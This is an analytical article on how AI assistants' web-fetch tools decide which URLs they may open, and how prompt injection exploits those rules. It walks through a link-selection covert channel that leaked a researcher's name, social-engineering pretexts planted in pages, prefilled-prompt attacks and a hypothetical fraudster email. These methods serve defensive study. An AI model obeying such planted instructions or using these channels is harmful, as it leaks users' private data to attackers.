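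Paul examined the everyday assistant at claude.ai. He wanted an attack that needed no experimental settings, code execution or connected services, so he was limited to Claude's web tools and its memory. According to Paul, the app condenses the user's recent conversations once a day into a few paragraphs, which it adds to every new conversation. Claude can also search the full history with a tool called conversation_search. Paul considered the memory system itself secure, and was interested in what happened when the same model could also browse the web.

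Oasis Security's *Claudy Day* describes a different attack on the app, in which the attacker can also reach conversation history and memory in a default session. These may include business strategy, financial information and health concerns. If the user has connected other services, the attacker may also be able to read files and send messages.

According to SiliconANGLE, Claude doesn't store information about sensitive subjects such as health, ethnicity, religion or political beliefs in its memory unless the user switches this on. But the chat app and Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, now share one memory, so Claude may have details from months of work in its memory when it reads a web page in a casual chat.

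### What Claude could open

Before the repair, the Claude app could open a URL if it appeared in the user's message, in web search results, or as a link on a page Claude had already fetched. Anthropic's fetch tool for developers accepts URLs from these sources and from the output of the developer's own tools. Paul's list of the app's sources doesn't include emails, so a link wouldn't have qualified just by appearing in a stranger's email, whereas ChatGPT accepted such links at the time of ZombieAgent.

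Links on fetched pages allowed Claude to move around a website as a person does, but they also allowed a hostile site to keep supplying new links.

Willison had been impressed by the fetch tool's design but calls this third source a loophole. However, Anthropic's developer documentation lists earlier fetch results as an accepted source, so the allowance was deliberate.

### Paul's tests

Paul first asked Claude to open a website he owned. The request failed because Cloudflare, a company that handles traffic for many websites, had added a robots.txt file with rules against automated visitors. After he fixed this, Claude's request appeared in his log. A site's owner can change the file, so it offers no protection against a hostile site.

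He then asked Claude to open an address on the site with his own name at the end. Anthropic's rule blocked the request, as intended, because Claude would have had to construct the URL.

dyb argues that Anthropic verified the wrong property, by making the tool read-only and overlooking what a URL's path can carry. The blocked request suggests otherwise. Anthropic had anticipated that a model might write private data into a path, and had prevented it. It had not prevented the model from choosing among paths that the attacker had written.

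Paul tested this with a page of links that each stood for a letter. He asked Claude to follow the link for the first letter of his name, and Claude chose correctly. He then had his server generate a new set of links after each choice, and Claude spelled out his first and last name in ten requests without constructing a URL. dyb calls this a covert channel, a term from a 1973 paper by Lampson for a path that nobody intended to carry information.

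Until then, Paul had given Claude the instructions himself. In a real attack they would have to come from the web page, and Claude was harder to persuade that way. Simple injected instructions worked unreliably, and several cover stories were too contrived. He succeeded with a pretext that made the task look like a routine requirement of the site. This fits OpenAI's observation that the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering. The site showed this page only to Claude, so a user who opened the same address in a browser would have seen an ordinary business website.

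Claude gave the site Paul's full name, his employer and his home city. Paul was extracting his own data, so the demonstration proves that the leak was possible but not how often the method would work on other people.

### A city that Claude worked out

Paul had never told Claude which city he came from. White Cloud Security's *The AI Is Now an Attack Surface* (2026) explains that Claude inferred it from the name of a hackathon he had started in high school. The name included "Queen City", a nickname for Charlotte, North Carolina.

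A home city is a common answer to websites' security questions. dyb advises users to read Claude's memory summary in the app's settings and delete whatever they wouldn't want an attacker to have. That is sensible, but a user checking for their home city might see only the name of a student event and not delete it.

Anthropic's limit on sensitive subjects has the same weakness. Claude might not store a user's religion, for example, but could perhaps infer it from the holidays they plan around.

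Inference also makes it harder to prevent leaks by searching outgoing requests for private data. Software can compare a URL with the names and addresses in a user's records, but those records may not include a fact the model has just inferred. The provenance rule doesn't have this problem, and would have blocked a constructed URL ending in "Charlotte" just as it blocked the one ending in Paul's name.

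### Anthropic's reply

Paul reported the flaw through Anthropic's bug bounty programme, which pays outside researchers for security findings. Anthropic replied that it had already found the problem internally, and it did not pay him, according to Willison. Anthropic then removed the fetch tool's ability to open links found on fetched pages.

Hackaday's *This Week In Security* gives a similar account and says that this prevents the attack "for now". But Hackaday, Willison and White Cloud Security all rely on Paul for what Anthropic told him, so they don't independently confirm it. None of them says when the repair was made, but it was in place by 15 July, when Willison wrote about it. White Cloud Security still described the rule the same way on 5 August.

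Companies often decline to pay for flaws they already know about, so the refusal isn't suspicious in itself. But outsiders can't check Anthropic's claim, and if it is true, the company had left a known leak unfixed in a product that holds people's conversation histories. Anthropic also had a public warning, because Radware had published ZombieAgent in January and OpenAI had restricted links from emails the month before.

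InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that Anthropic favours deterministic limits on an agent's files, network and execution environment over relying solely on permission prompts or safeguards in the model. Anthropic also examined cases in which data could leave by routes it had permitted, and revised its designs in response. The fix to the fetch tool follows the same approach, since Anthropic removed the route instead of relying on Claude to recognise the next pretext.

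### What changed, and what Anthropic could have done instead

| What Claude tries to open in the app | Before the repair | After the repair |
|---|---|---|
| An address in the user's message | Allowed | Allowed |
| A search result | Allowed | Allowed |
| A link that appears only on a fetched page | Allowed | Blocked |
| A link on a fetched page that a search also returned | Allowed | Allowed |
| An address to which Claude has added the user's name | Blocked | Blocked |

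If Claude visited Paul's site now, it could still open the first page and might still believe the pretext. But it couldn't open any of the links, so the site's owner would learn only that Claude had visited.

Two milder restrictions would still have let an attacker extract data. Letting Claude follow links for only one step would have stopped the chain of pages, but the attacker decides how many links to put on the first page. With 10,000 links, a single choice could reveal about 13 bits, and Claude could return to the same list to make another choice. Restricting Claude to links within the same website would not have helped, because Paul's links all led to his own site.

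dyb suggests letting Claude follow links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. This would protect a user whose search happened to turn up a hostile site. It wouldn't protect someone who asked Claude to look at that site, as dyb acknowledges, and people do ask about unfamiliar businesses.

dyb also proposes software that watches for Paul's pattern, a rapid series of requests to one domain in which each path is one character longer than the last. Ordinary browsing can look similar, so dyb would require several signs at once to avoid false alarms. The more serious problem is that the attacker writes the URLs and can choose ones that don't follow the pattern.

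Anthropic's fix is more reliable than any of these because it doesn't require software to recognise a bad site or a suspicious sequence. But it also blocks harmless links, such as those from a table of contents to the chapters.

The blogger dyb argues more broadly that Anthropic closes one route at a time while each new tool creates more. dyb lists six disclosures involving Claude products between October 2025 and July 2026, but most concern other routes, including file uploads and a leak of API keys from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. The list is good evidence that an assistant with many tools has many ways to leak data, but only Paul's case is evidence about the fetch rule. In that case Anthropic removed a whole source of links, which does more than blocking one attacker's site or one phrasing.

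### Search results as a narrower channel

Attackers might still be able to use search results after the fix. As with OpenAI's index, they would have to publish their pages in advance and get them indexed. To repeat Paul's leak, they would also need several of those pages to appear in the results when Claude searches during the victim's conversation.

This last condition makes the app's rule stricter than OpenAI's index rule for pages that an attacker prepares in advance. An attacker with 4,096 indexed pages can use all of them against ChatGPT, but can use only those that a search has returned against Claude.

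If a search returns three of the attacker's pages, Claude's choice among them reveals at most 1.6 bits, compared with 4.75 bits for a choice among the 27 links on each of Paul's pages. Claude would need 30 fetches to convey the ten characters that took ten fetches in his test.

The attacker may not be limited to three pages, though, because Claude writes its own search queries. An attacker whose page has persuaded Claude could instruct it to search for their other pages, and Claude could then fetch every URL in the results. With enough searches, the attacker might be able to use most of their indexed pages, which would bring the limit closer to OpenAI's. At each search, however, Claude could refuse or the search engine could leave the pages out. This is an inference from the rule, as Paul's published tests used links on fetched pages instead.

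White Cloud Security mentions a related possibility that Paul raised but did not test. An attacker could publish a high-ranking page about a current news story so that people who ask Claude about the story come across it. This would expose more users to the hostile instructions, but the attacker would still need other admitted URLs to get much data out.

The fetch rule doesn't restrict the wording of searches, so a manipulated model could put the user's name in a query, for instance. But the query would go to the search provider, whose logs the attacker normally can't read. That makes it much less useful to the attacker than a request to their own server.

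Claude also selects images from web search results and displays them next to its answer, using Microsoft's Bing, according to Anthropic's *Enabling and using web search*. If the user's browser loads an image directly from the original website, the choice of image could reveal something to that site's owner, just as a choice of page does. The owner would receive no request if the browser loaded a copy from Bing or Anthropic instead.

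In a turn capped at five fetches, with three of the attacker's pages in the search results, Claude could reveal at most about 8 bits. That could be enough to convey the user's age, but usually not their full name.

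## What counts as supplied by the user

In the Claude app, a user can have Claude open any page by putting the address in a message, even if no search has returned that address. ChatGPT has a similar exception for addresses missing from OpenAI's index. An assistant that refused to open pages its user asked about would be of little use, and the rules rest on the assumption that an attacker doesn't control what the user types. But a user's message often contains text that the user didn't type, and OpenAI and Anthropic have published little about whether links in that text count as supplied by the user.

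### Nine link sources compared

In the table, "indexed only" means that ChatGPT loads the URL without asking the user only if OpenAI's crawler has recorded it. "Undocumented" marks cases that the published descriptions don't settle. The API column gives the default settings of the ordinary API, not of Managed Agents.

| Link source | ChatGPT | Anthropic's API | Claude app | Can an attacker write there? |
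|---|---|---|---|---|
| Text the user types | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted | Only by persuading the user |
| Text the user pastes | Undocumented, probably accepted | Accepted | Undocumented, probably accepted | Yes, if someone else wrote the text |
| Uploaded files | Indexed only, unless a file counts as the user's message (undocumented) | Undocumented | Undocumented | Yes, if someone else wrote the file |
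| Connected email and documents | Indexed only | Accepted from the developer's own tool, rejected from the MCP connector | Undocumented, but not on Paul's list | Yes |
| Client-side tool results | No equivalent | Accepted | No equivalent | Yes, if the tool returns outside text |
| Memory | Indexed only | Depends on where the developer puts it | Undocumented, but not on Paul's list | Yes, indirectly |
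| Search results | Indexed only | Accepted | Accepted | Yes, by publishing pages that a search returns |
| Fetched pages | Indexed only | Accepted | Rejected since July 2026 | Yes |
| Public index | Accepted | Not an accepted source | Not an accepted source | Yes, by publishing pages in advance |

Several entries for ChatGPT are inferences. OpenAI doesn't mention files, Memory or connected accounts in its January post, but it describes a test for any URL the agent is about to retrieve automatically, so the test should cover links from all three. ChatGPT may still refuse all links from Memory, as Radware saw it do in 2025.

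The post doesn't mention an exception for links in the user's own messages either. Evidence for the exception comes from *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, which describes links "provided directly by the user in a chat prompt", and from Rehberger, who writes on Embrace The Red of URLs "directly entered as part of a user message". Paul uses similar words for the Claude app. None of them defines "directly", which could cover every link in an email that the user pastes in.

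### A user message in the API

For developers, "user message" is a technical term. A developer's program assembles a list of messages, each labelled with a role, and sends the whole list to Anthropic's API. The role "assistant" marks what Claude wrote, and "user" marks the program's own messages to Claude.

Anthropic's software can therefore detect that a URL appeared in a user message, but not how it got there. The label "user" only identifies a position in the data format, so a person may have typed the URL, or the program that sent the message may have copied it from a database with no person involved.

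Claude can't fetch a URL that appears only in the system prompt, so Anthropic tells developers to repeat it in a user message, although no user has written or seen it. This advice is harmless because the developer chose the address, but it relies on programs being able to add text to user messages.

Other parts of the documentation suggest a narrower meaning. In June 2026, Anthropic warned in its documentation that Claude could fetch only URLs "explicitly provided by the user" or returned by an earlier search or fetch. Further down the same page, it also listed the results of the developer's own tools as an accepted source. A developer who read only the warning might reasonably have concluded that Claude would never open a link from a stranger's email, but it could if one of the developer's tools had returned the email.

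Willison objected to the rule on these grounds on 10 September 2025, the day Anthropic released the tool. He wrote that in many applications vulnerable to prompt injection, developers combine untrusted text with their own instructions in the user message. They do so because it is easy. For example, a program that summarizes documents can insert each document into a fixed instruction and send the result as one message.

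This is the developer's mistake, since only the developer knows which parts of the message came from outside. But Anthropic's wording encouraged it, and its API documentation described no way to exclude user messages as a source until the second half of 2026, when it added the url_sources setting.

Willison's objection doesn't affect the ban on constructed URLs. An attacker whose text ends up in a user message can supply complete URLs for Claude to choose from, but can't make Claude add private data to them.

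### A support tool that inserts an email

Suppose the invented company Widget gives its support staff a program that drafts replies to customers. An employee opens an email and presses a button, and the program sends Claude a single user message with four parts:

| Part of the message | Who wrote it |
|---|---|
| An instruction to draft a reply | Widget's developer |
| The customer's account record, including whether Widget suspects fraud | Widget's staff |
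| The text of the email | Anyone who writes to the support address |
| An optional remark | The employee |

The employee may not have typed anything. Suppose the email comes from a fraudster who wants to know whether Widget has become suspicious. It contains two links to the fraudster's site, with text that leads Claude to open one if Widget has flagged the account and the other if it hasn't. Both URLs appear in a user message, so the API allows Claude to fetch either one. The fraudster can see which link Claude opened, and that one bit of information reveals whether Widget has flagged the account.

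Putting everything in one message also weakens Anthropic's separate check for credentials, which exempts any that appear in the text of a user message. The exemption then covers a password in the customer's email or the account record. The provenance rule would normally still block a URL containing that password. But if Widget also lets Claude run code through a client-side tool and keeps the default settings, the code can print such a URL, which then passes both checks.

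Widget could set user_input to "none", which would exclude the fraudster's links. That setting would also exclude any address the employee typed in the remark, because developers can't filter a user message by its parts.

Widget would do better to take the email out of the user message. It could write a tool that returns the email when Claude calls it, and set client_tool_results to "none". Claude would read the same text, but the API would reject the links in it, and the employee could still type an address for Claude to open. The program could instead strip the links from the email before inserting it, but it would then have to recognise every form of URL that Anthropic's software does.

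The fraudster's instructions could still distort the draft reply, so the employee should read it before sending it.

### Links the user pasted without reading

Chat app users can create the same problem by pasting text. Suppose a user pastes a newsletter into ChatGPT and asks for a summary. The newsletter contains 30 links to the sender's website, and the user has read none of them. If ChatGPT had found the newsletter through a connected email account, the December 2025 restriction would have kept it from opening any unindexed link. But because the user pasted the text, ChatGPT probably treats all 30 links as supplied by the user, even though the sender wrote them.

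Five fetches from 30 links could reveal about 24.5 bits, more than enough for a six-digit login code. But the sender can't add links after the user has pasted the text, whereas a website can generate new ones at every step.

The links may remain usable for the rest of the chat in programs that use Anthropic's API and, if Rehberger's impression is right, in ChatGPT. A user could paste a newsletter in the morning and discuss a medical result in the same chat that afternoon. The assistant would then have something much more private to reveal, while the sender's links and instructions would still be in the conversation.

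How the app handles pasted text also matters, because the address in many emails sits behind words such as "View invoice". If the app keeps only the visible words, the URL never enters the conversation. That would remove many links from ordinary newsletters, but an attacker can write the addresses out in full.

One argument for accepting pasted links anyway is that the attacker has to wait for the user to paste something, whereas an assistant connected to an inbox may read the attacker's email as soon as the user asks about the day's messages. Pasting also suggests some interest in the contents. But people have good reason to paste a message they distrust and ask whether it is a scam. They want the assistant to examine the links, and would probably be alarmed to learn that it had opened them.

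### Prompts that arrive through a link

A user can also send a message written entirely by someone else. Web addresses for ChatGPT and Claude can contain the text of a prompt, so that a link opens a new chat with the prompt already filled in. This is useful for shortcuts, but it also lets an attacker write the user's message.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) reports that ChatGPT filled in the text and submitted it as soon as the page loaded, so a user who clicked the link had no chance to read the prompt first. An attacker could use the prompt to have ChatGPT summarize a hostile website, whose pages then supplied further instructions. The attacker could also choose the model and turn on search through the same link.

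The hostile site's address would count as supplied by the user under a rule that trusts URLs in user messages. Tenable didn't test such a rule, but its finding undermines the assumption behind the exception that the attacker doesn't control the user's side of the chat.

OpenAI took 87 days to settle on a fix. Tenable reported the flaw on 15 April 2025, and OpenAI had released a first fix to all users by 30 April. On 6 May Tenable noticed that the problem persisted, and two days later OpenAI asked Tenable for ideas. On 11 July OpenAI replied that it had improved safe_url, its check on links, and added protections against automatic submission based on the sec-fetch-site header. Browsers use this header to show whether a request came from the same website, a different one, or the user directly, for instance through a bookmark. OpenAI can therefore detect that another website sent the user to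 ChatGPT, and wait before submitting the prompt.

The header is a sensible signal because the browser sets it, so code on an attacker's page can't change it. But it indicates how the user arrived, not who wrote the prompt. Clicking a link in a desktop email program may look like a direct visit, since no website started the request.

Anthropic also had trouble with prefilled prompts. *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) describes the attack on the Claude app that Oasis Security named Claudy Day. A link filled the message box with a harmless request and instructions that the box didn't display. When the user pressed Enter, Claude received both. The hidden instructions appeared in the chat only after the user had sent them. Anthropic has since fixed this.

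In that attack, the data left through a file upload, not the fetch tool. According to Luz, Claude could use the fetch tool only from the second exchange onwards, and its safety training also made it decline suspicious addresses. The delay would have given limited protection against planted links, because a URL in the first message is still in the conversation when the user sends the second.

In July 2026, Oasis Security disclosed a more direct version in Claude Desktop, Anthropic's app for computers. *PromptFiction* (Luz, 2026) describes a link that opened the app and made Claude act on a prompt without the user pressing send. Luz blames the system for accepting a prompt with "no proof that a human wrote it or agreed to send it." After Anthropic's fix, the prompt stays in the message box until the user sends it.

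The fix restores the user's agreement, but an attacker may still have written the prompt. Claudy Day succeeded even though the user pressed Enter. Even when a long prompt is fully visible, a user may well read only the opening lines and miss a list of links at the end.

### Three possible definitions

A company could define a user-supplied URL as one that a person typed, one that appears anywhere in the user's turn, or one that the user confirmed. In the table, confirming means approving that particular URL in a separate dialogue, not just sending a message that contains it.

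| How the URL arrives | Typed by a person | In the user's turn | Confirmed by the user |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user types it | Admitted | Admitted | The software asks |
| The user pastes it alone | Blocked | Admitted | The software asks |
| The user pastes it in an email with 29 other links | Blocked | Admitted | The software asks |
| A support tool inserts it with a customer's email | Blocked | Admitted | The software asks the employee |
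| It is in a prefilled prompt that the user sends | Blocked | Admitted | The software asks |
| A program inserts it overnight, with nobody present | Blocked | Admitted | Blocked, as nobody can answer |

A rule that counted only typed addresses would give the best protection. An attacker might persuade someone to type one address, but probably not 37, and with only one address, the assistant has nothing to choose between. But the rule would also reject most of the links that people deliberately share, because hardly anyone types out a long URL. Anthropic also couldn't enforce it in its API, because only the company that runs the message box can tell typing from pasting.

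ChatGPT, the Claude app and Anthropic's API all appear to accept any URL in the user's turn. Software can easily check whether a URL meets this rule, and users can predict the result. The rule also allows every case in the table, including the four in which the user may never have looked at the URL.

OpenAI already asks the user to confirm a URL that isn't in the index. Confirmation helps most when the user can recognise private data in the URL, but a provenance rule already blocks most such URLs. In a selection leak, the URL contains no such data. Widget's employee would see one of two ordinary-looking addresses, and approving either would give the fraudster an answer. Ten requests in a row to open nearly identical addresses would look strange, but one or two wouldn't. Asking about every link would also encourage the habitual clicking that OpenAI wants to avoid.

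A chat app could combine these definitions by accepting addresses that the user types and links pasted on their own, since the user has chosen a particular page in both cases. It could treat links in a longer pasted passage like links in an email. ChatGPT would then open them only if they are in the index, and otherwise try another site or show the warning. Users would need one more step to open a private link from a long message, which seems a minor inconvenience.

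In the API, only the developer can identify which part of a user message came from the user. Anthropic could let developers mark that part and restrict user_input to it. Some developers would mark the wrong part or forget, but they would at least be able to follow the rule that "explicitly provided by the user" seems to describe.

### Sources that attackers can still reach

By default, every rule now in use accepts links from at least one source that an attacker can influence. OpenAI accepts any page that an attacker has managed to get into its index. In the Claude app, Anthropic no longer accepts links on fetched pages, but Willison reports that it still accepts search results, and attackers can publish pages for a search to find. Anthropic's API accepts links from both fetched pages and search results by default, along with any that the developer's program puts into a user message.

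A developer can now get much closer to the stricter rule Willison hoped for in 2025 by using url_sources to set client_tool_results and server_tool_results to "none", which leaves only the URLs in user messages. If those messages contain only what a person typed, Claude can open only the addresses that person chose. But if people can also paste text into them, whoever wrote that text can again supply links.

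## Checks in the backend and instructions to the model

Once a company has decided which link sources to accept, it can apply the rule in two ways. It can instruct or train the model to fetch only the exact URLs it was given. Or it can use *backend enforcement*, storing those URLs and having ordinary code outside the model check each request against them. The two methods may look the same in everyday use, but they behave very differently under attack.

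### Why an instruction can fail

The text of an attacker's page can influence whether the model follows an instruction, for example by presenting the forbidden request as an exception or as something the user wanted. Such wording doesn't affect the result of code that compares URLs.

Repeated attempts also help the attacker when the defence is an instruction. If the model obeys the instruction 99% of the time, the chance of at least one leak over 100 independent attempts is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. An exact comparison in code gives the same result on every attempt, which also means that an attacker who finds a bug in the code can use it every time.

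A model can also break the instruction when no attacker is involved, by miscopying a long URL or guessing one from the pattern of other URLs.

### The check in pseudocode

A simple version for a rule that accepts URLs from the conversation could look like this:

```
allowed = empty table    # normalised URL -> URL as the source gave it

when text enters the conversation:
    if the text came from an accepted link source:
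        for each url in the text:
            allowed[normalise(url)] = url

when the model asks to fetch a url:
    key = normalise(url)
    if key is not in allowed:
        return "refused: not from an accepted source"
    page = request(allowed[key], follow_redirects = no)
    if page is a redirect:
        return "redirect not followed"
    return page
```

For OpenAI's rule that a URL must already be public, the crawler's record would take the place of most of the first half. Normalising means converting harmless variants of a URL, such as `Shop.example` and `shop.example`, to one standard form. Each step can err in either direction:

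| Step | Error that allows a leak | Error that blocks a harmless page |
|---|---|---|
| Collect | The code treats a stranger's text as the user's | The code stores the full stop after a URL at the end of a sentence |
| Normalise | The code drops the query string | The code treats capitals in a domain name as significant |
| Compare | The code checks only how the URL begins | The code loses the stored set when a program trims old messages |
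| Fetch | The code follows a redirect without checking the destination | The code refuses a redirect within the same site |
| Refuse | The error repeats the URL, and the code then collects it | The error gives no reason, so the model gives up |

The first error in the table is the one Willison objected to in Anthropic's API, where developers often put untrusted text into user messages. No later step can correct it, because the code has already stored the attacker's URL as allowed.

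Checking only the beginning of a URL can let through a request to the wrong server. If the stored URL is `https://shop.example`, a request for `https://shop.example.attacker.example` passes the check but goes to a server controlled by the owner of attacker.example.

The pseudocode requests the stored URL instead of the model's version, which prevents the leak through capital letters described earlier. The code that compares URLs and the code that sends the request should also use the same parsed address, to avoid the Unicode mismatches that Anthropic describes in its warning about look-alike domains.

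Refusing every redirect is safe but inconvenient, since many sites forward visitors to a slightly different address. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* (2025), an independent analysis, describes a more practical policy in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Its fetch tool automatically follows redirects within the same host. If a redirect leads to another host, the tool returns information about it, and Claude has to make a new call to continue. Under a provenance rule, the new call should go through the same comparison as any other. Otherwise, the model decides whether to follow the redirect.

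The loop in the last row occurs when tool results count as a link source and the error message contains the refused URL. The model's second attempt then succeeds, because the URL has appeared in a tool result. The example error in Anthropic's documentation contains only an error code, which avoids the loop.

### What instructions are still good for

Instructions can make a rule easier to work with. A model told that it can't construct URLs will waste fewer calls on requests the code will refuse. When a user names a document without giving its URL, Claude usually searches for it first, which also adds the URL to those it may fetch.

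Instructions also help the model decide what to do after the code refuses a URL, such as searching for the page, using another source, or telling the user what it couldn't open. If the model asks the user for the address, it should not suggest one. If it writes out a URL it constructed and the user pastes it back, the code will find that URL in a user message and allow it.

An error message can contain this guidance too. *ChatGPT Containers can now run bash, pip/npm install packages, and download files* (Willison, 2026) describes a ChatGPT tool that saves files from the web into a container, an isolated environment for running code. When ChatGPT tried to download from a URL it had constructed, it reportedly received an error message that the URL had not been "viewed in conversation before", with an instruction to open it with its web tool first. The download tool's check therefore depends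 on how strict the web tool is.

Training matters more against selection leaks, because they pass an exact comparison and the model's refusal is one of the few remaining obstacles. OpenAI relies on training to stop most attacks and on Safe Url to stop the rest. This is reasonable for content leaks, but Safe Url can't detect a leak made by choosing among an attacker's indexed pages. OpenAI describes the URL check as one layer among several, along with training, product controls, monitoring and continuing tests by people who try to break the system.

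### What outsiders found in the products

In September 2025, when Anthropic released the fetch tool for developers, Willison found that switching on web search in the Claude app also gave it web_fetch. Using a server that displayed incoming requests, he tested whether Claude could fetch a URL it had constructed, and it couldn't. He presumed that the software required the URL to exactly match one in the user's prompt. Paul got the same result in 2026 when he asked Claude to add his name to an address.

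These tests were small, and a missing request doesn't by itself show whether the model declined to make it or code blocked it, since the server's log is empty either way. Anthropic's documentation is better evidence of backend enforcement, because it says the tool "cannot fetch arbitrary URLs that Claude generates" and, since August 2026, has listed a separate error code for such refusals.

In Willison's tests of ChatGPT in January 2026, the download tool rejected his constructed URL, but the separate web tool opened one with a simple constructed query string. A filter blocked a longer query string containing his previous prompts. He concluded that the feature was probably safe, but wondered how it would hold up against an experienced security researcher.

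That conclusion seems a little generous. A short query string can hold a login code or a surname, and a filter based on length or content is easier to get around than an exact comparison. Two days later, OpenAI published its rule that a URL must already be public. Willison doesn't give the URL that passed, so it isn't clear whether the web tool was still using an older check or allowed the URL for another reason.

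### An experiment with both kinds of defence

In a controlled experiment, *Silent Egress* compared instructions to the model with checks outside it. Four researchers at eBay built an assistant around qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a page, and the model had a secret in its context and a tool for making web requests.

The main experiment varied where the hidden instruction was (the page's title, description, body or link text), whether the assistant reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the instruction required sending the secret whole or in four pieces. Each of the 16 combinations had 30 runs, and the assistant sent data to the researchers' collection server in 423 of the 480 runs. In 120 further runs with harmless pages, it never contacted that server.

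The researchers then tested defences on the simplest combination, with the instruction in the body of a page that the assistant opened directly. Each row represents 30 runs:

| Defence | Model attempted the request | Data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Instruction never to obey web content | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
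| List of allowed domains | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |
| All of these | 0% | 0% |

The instruction helped, but the model still leaked the secret in two thirds of the runs. At that rate, an attacker with three independent attempts would succeed at least once about 96% of the time. Marking the untrusted text with tags made no difference by itself. Using both prevented only three more leaks in 30 runs than the instruction alone, which could easily be chance.

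The row for allowed domains is the best example of backend enforcement. The model attempted the leak in all 30 runs, and the code stopped it every time. This result isn't surprising, since the researchers deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was clearly not on the list. They caution that real attackers could use a compromised site or a redirect from a trusted one.

The other filters deserve less confidence. The filter for suspicious addresses blocks any path containing the word "collect", which appears in the study's own example of a collection address, but a real attacker would pick another word. The attempt rates for the last two filters are also hard to explain, because a filter that acts after the model has written a request shouldn't affect how often the model writes one. The researchers suggest that the model avoided random-looking values while the filter was active, but they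 don't explain how the model could have detected the filter.

The researchers acknowledge that their study favours the attacker. They placed the secret directly in the model's context, gave the model few other instructions, and tested only one model. They argue that stronger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. That is possible, but it doesn't fit OpenAI's experience with crude commands or ChatGPT's result in *The Framing Gap*. We can therefore infer little about ChatGPT or Claude from the percentages. A check outside the model should still have an advantage with those assistants, since it doesn't depend on which model makes the request.

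The researchers did not test a provenance rule, but they propose a related method called taint tracking, in which software marks web text as untrusted and follows its influence through the system. If marked text influenced a web request, the software could block the request, ask the user, or record it for review. In principle this would also catch selection leaks, because the attacker's page influenced the choice of link. But a language model draws on its whole context, so after it had read one web page, nearly every later request might carry the mark.

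### Apps and screens without the check

A backend check protects only requests that go through it. OpenAI's url_safe check didn't protect the company's Mac and phone apps at first, because each app's code had to call the check and act on the result. OpenAI released a fix for the Mac app in 2024, according to Embrace The Red.

Claude's iPhone app had a similar gap. Anthropic had already fixed the image flaw elsewhere in Claude, but it did not fix a data leak in the app until December 2024. According to the announcement, which Willison (2024) reproduced, mobile apps often have the same problem with images.

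PromptArmor found that data could also leak through OpenAI's log viewer for developers, which displayed images from model responses insecurely. If an app flagged a suspicious response for review, a developer who opened the log could trigger the request that the app had avoided. OpenAI confirmed the flaw and said it was working on a fix.

After OpenAI published its technical paper in 2026, Rehberger warned on Embrace The Red that some of the company's developers might not know about Safe Url or adopt it. A flaw in the Codex desktop app for Mac soon gave his warning some support. NVD's *CVE-2026-14898* (2026), an entry in the US government's database of software flaws, describes how the app automatically loaded outside images from the model's responses. An attacker could use this to obtain API keys, source code, or data from connected tools. OpenAI supplied the record, which NVD published in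 July, and knew of no real attacks. The record doesn't explain why the app lacked an effective check, so it can't confirm that the developers were unaware of Safe Url.

URL checks are easier to enforce for fetch tools than for images. If a company's own servers make the fetch requests, the company can put the check where requests leave its network, so no app can skip it. Images load on users' devices, through apps that different teams may have written. The company could still make those apps block outside images by default. Then, if a team forgot the check, outside images wouldn't load and no data would leave.

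### Code that can reach the network

If an assistant can run a program with network access, that program can contact a server without calling the fetch tool, so the provenance rule doesn't apply. The same is true when a developer gives Claude a command-line tool on a computer connected to the internet. Limits on web_fetch, including a list of allowed domains, don't restrict which servers Claude's commands can contact.

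OpenAI blocks ordinary outbound requests from ChatGPT's container. Willison found that ChatGPT could still install software packages there because OpenAI provides a *proxy*, an intermediary server that passes on package requests. Useful exceptions like this need their own restrictions.

Blocking ordinary requests didn't always prevent leaks. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reports that the leak of messages and files OpenAI fixed in February 2026 used a hidden route out of the container. The model treated the container as closed, so it didn't identify the route as a way to send data.

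## What users and developers lose

The rules also block requests that aren't part of an attack. Many websites rely on unpublished addresses, such as the URL of a product search or a customer's download link. A person can open them in a browser, but an assistant under a URL provenance rule often can't.

### Six ordinary tasks

The table assumes the user hasn't put the address in a message. For ChatGPT, "blocked" means it tries another website or shows the warning.

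| Task | ChatGPT | Anthropic's API, default settings | Claude app |
|---|---|---|---|
| Open the next page of results | Blocked unless the crawler recorded it | Allowed if the first page links to it | Blocked unless a search returns it |
| Query a public data service | Blocked unless the crawler recorded that exact query | Blocked unless an accepted source contains that exact query | Blocked unless a search returns that exact query |
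| Open a manual page by guessing its address | Allowed if the crawler recorded it, which is likely | Blocked until a search or another page supplies it | Blocked until a search returns it |
| Open a page published minutes ago | Blocked until the crawler finds it | Allowed if a fetched page links to it | Blocked until a search returns it |
| Open a private document link from an email | Blocked | Depends on which tool read the email | Undocumented, probably blocked |
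| Open a signed download link of 400 characters from an email | Blocked | Blocked by the length limit | Undocumented, probably blocked |

A signed link is an address that a storage service issues for one file. It is long because it includes an expiry time and a code proving that the holder may download the file.

Products differ in what they show the user. In ChatGPT, the user either sees the warning or may never learn that the next page of results or a new article was missing.

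In apps built on Anthropic's API, the user sees only what Claude writes after a fetch is refused, which might be an explanation, a result from another site, or an answer based on less evidence. The developer can miss the refusal too, because Anthropic returns the error inside a response with status 200, the web's code for success, and software that counts only failed API requests won't register it. Anthropic doesn't document a warning in the Claude app like the one in ChatGPT, so the app's users also depend on Claude to explain.

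An assistant may be unable to fetch the next page of results even where the rule accepts links on fetched pages. Many sites use JavaScript to load more results when the visitor presses a button, and Anthropic's fetch tool doesn't support pages built that way. Claude then has no link to copy, and the API rejects any address Claude guesses.

Most of these obstacles disappear if the user supplies the URL. For *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026) asked AI services about test pages they had just created. OpenAI's and Anthropic's APIs and the ChatGPT and Claude apps all loaded the pages when the question contained the URL. A crawler is very unlikely to have found those pages beforehand, so the result also supports reports that ChatGPT makes an exception for URLs in the user's message. Supplying the URL doesn't help with the signed link in Anthropic's API, because the API refuses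 any URL over 250 characters.

### One research task under three policies

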